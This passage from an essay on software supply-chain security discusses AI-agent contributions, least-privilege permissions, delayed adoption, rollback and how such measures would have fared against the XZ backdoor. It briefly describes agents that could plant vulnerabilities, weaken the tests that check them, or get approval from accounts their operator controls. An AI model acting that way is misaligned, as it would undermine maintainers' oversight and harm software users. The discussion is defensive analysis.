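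Defenders of the rules can reply that the volume of pull requests is itself a security problem, since maintainers with fewer to read can spend longer on each one. Requiring disclosure also lets maintainers stop accepting work from a contributor who lies about using an agent, without having to prove malice or find a vulnerability. Making contributors responsible for their own changes helps in the same way, because they can no longer excuse a flaw by saying that a model wrote the code.

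The reply is convincing for disclosure and limits on volume, but less so for outright bans. In 2025 the curl project complained that it was overwhelmed by worthless AI-written vulnerability reports. By April 2026, its leader Daniel Stenberg said these had stopped and the project was receiving more and more good reports, nearly all written with AI's help. Those were bug reports rather than code changes, but a ban on AI would have excluded the good ones too. A project that wants to keep such help has to judge the work itself, and it still needs a way to handle its mistakes.

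### Limiting the damage

The first precaution is to give an agent only the access its task requires. Besides having limited pipeline permissions, it should not be able to publish releases, change branch protection or edit the security tests that check its work. An agent with these limits can still write a vulnerability, but it can't remove the safeguards against releasing it.

Datadog had several layers of protection when hackerbot-claw attacked its repositories. The attacker got code to run in one workflow but then faced further controls, according to a summary of the company's account in the newsletter tl;dr sec. An AI system that reviews Datadog's code changes also helped detect the attack.

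An agent shouldn't approve its own changes or those of another agent that the same person controls. The July agent's supporter on myNetwork was a different account but not an independent reviewer. To prevent this, a project has to count the people responsible for the accounts, which is harder than counting accounts.

**Delayed adoption** means waiting before using any new release. StepSecurity offers a similar waiting period for pipeline components. The delay can protect a program's users when its maintainers have missed something. Kennedy Toomey of Datadog argues for such "cooldowns", according to tl;dr sec.

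How much a delay helps depends on how long the attack stays hidden. A one-day delay would have been more than enough to avoid the backdoored LiteLLM packages, while avoiding the XZ backdoor would have taken about five weeks. A well-disguised vulnerability might stay hidden for years, so a short delay gives little protection against planted vulnerabilities.

If everyone waited to adopt new releases, fewer people would notice problems in them. Automated scanners partly solve this because they can examine a package without anyone adopting it. But Freund discovered the XZ backdoor because his test installations were already running the compromised version. Some people need to run new versions early, preferably on machines with nothing valuable on them.

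Delays also hold back security fixes. An organisation can exempt urgent fixes, but this gives attackers a reason to describe a malicious release as an urgent fix. Someone should confirm that the release fixes a real vulnerability before the organisation skips the wait.

**Rollback** means returning to an earlier safe version. It is much faster if the project has recorded which commit each release came from, because the maintainers can then identify every affected release. They can undo an ordinary bad change by adding a commit that reverses it. Deleting the original commit would change the identifiers of all later commits and could break other projects that refer to them.

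If a project reverses the change too soon after an attack like PolinRider, the malware may put its code back, and the evidence of how it arrived may be lost. Smith recommends first preserving the logs and the infected copy, isolating the machines that can write to the repository, and revoking stolen credentials. The project should then restore the code from a clean machine and rebuild everything it released in the meantime.

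Users still have to install the replacement. The agent's change to Anaconda had already gone out in a release when the team reverted it. A vulnerability discovered after three years is even harder to undo, because nobody will want to lose three years of other improvements by returning to an earlier version. The maintainers then have to write a fix and publish it quickly.

### The same measures applied to XZ Utils

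| Measure | Likely effect on the XZ attack |
|---|---|
| Signed commits and releases | None, because the attacker's signatures were genuine |
| Second approval | Some, but Collin would have been approving unreadable test files |
| Hosted build with attestation | Would have exposed the altered script or forced it into the repository, if distributions had refused other downloads |
| Reproducible builds | Useful only if someone started from the repository |
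| Anomalicious | Probably none, because the author had a long record |
| Ban on force-pushes | None, because the attack did not depend on rewriting history |
| Rules for AI contributions | None |
| Delayed adoption | Useful only after a wait of about five weeks, with others still testing |
| Rollback | Effective, but only after Freund's discovery |

SLSA could have done slightly more against the XZ backdoor than a draft of its threat list suggests. The draft classes XZ as the work of a producer with a good reputation who intentionally released malicious code, a threat mostly outside the standard's scope. But if a hosted service had built the release from the repository, Jia Tan would have had to commit the altered script, and a second-approval rule would have required Collin to approve it. He might have missed the change, as he may have missed the Landlock typo, but the script was text he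 could have read and questioned, unlike the binary test files.
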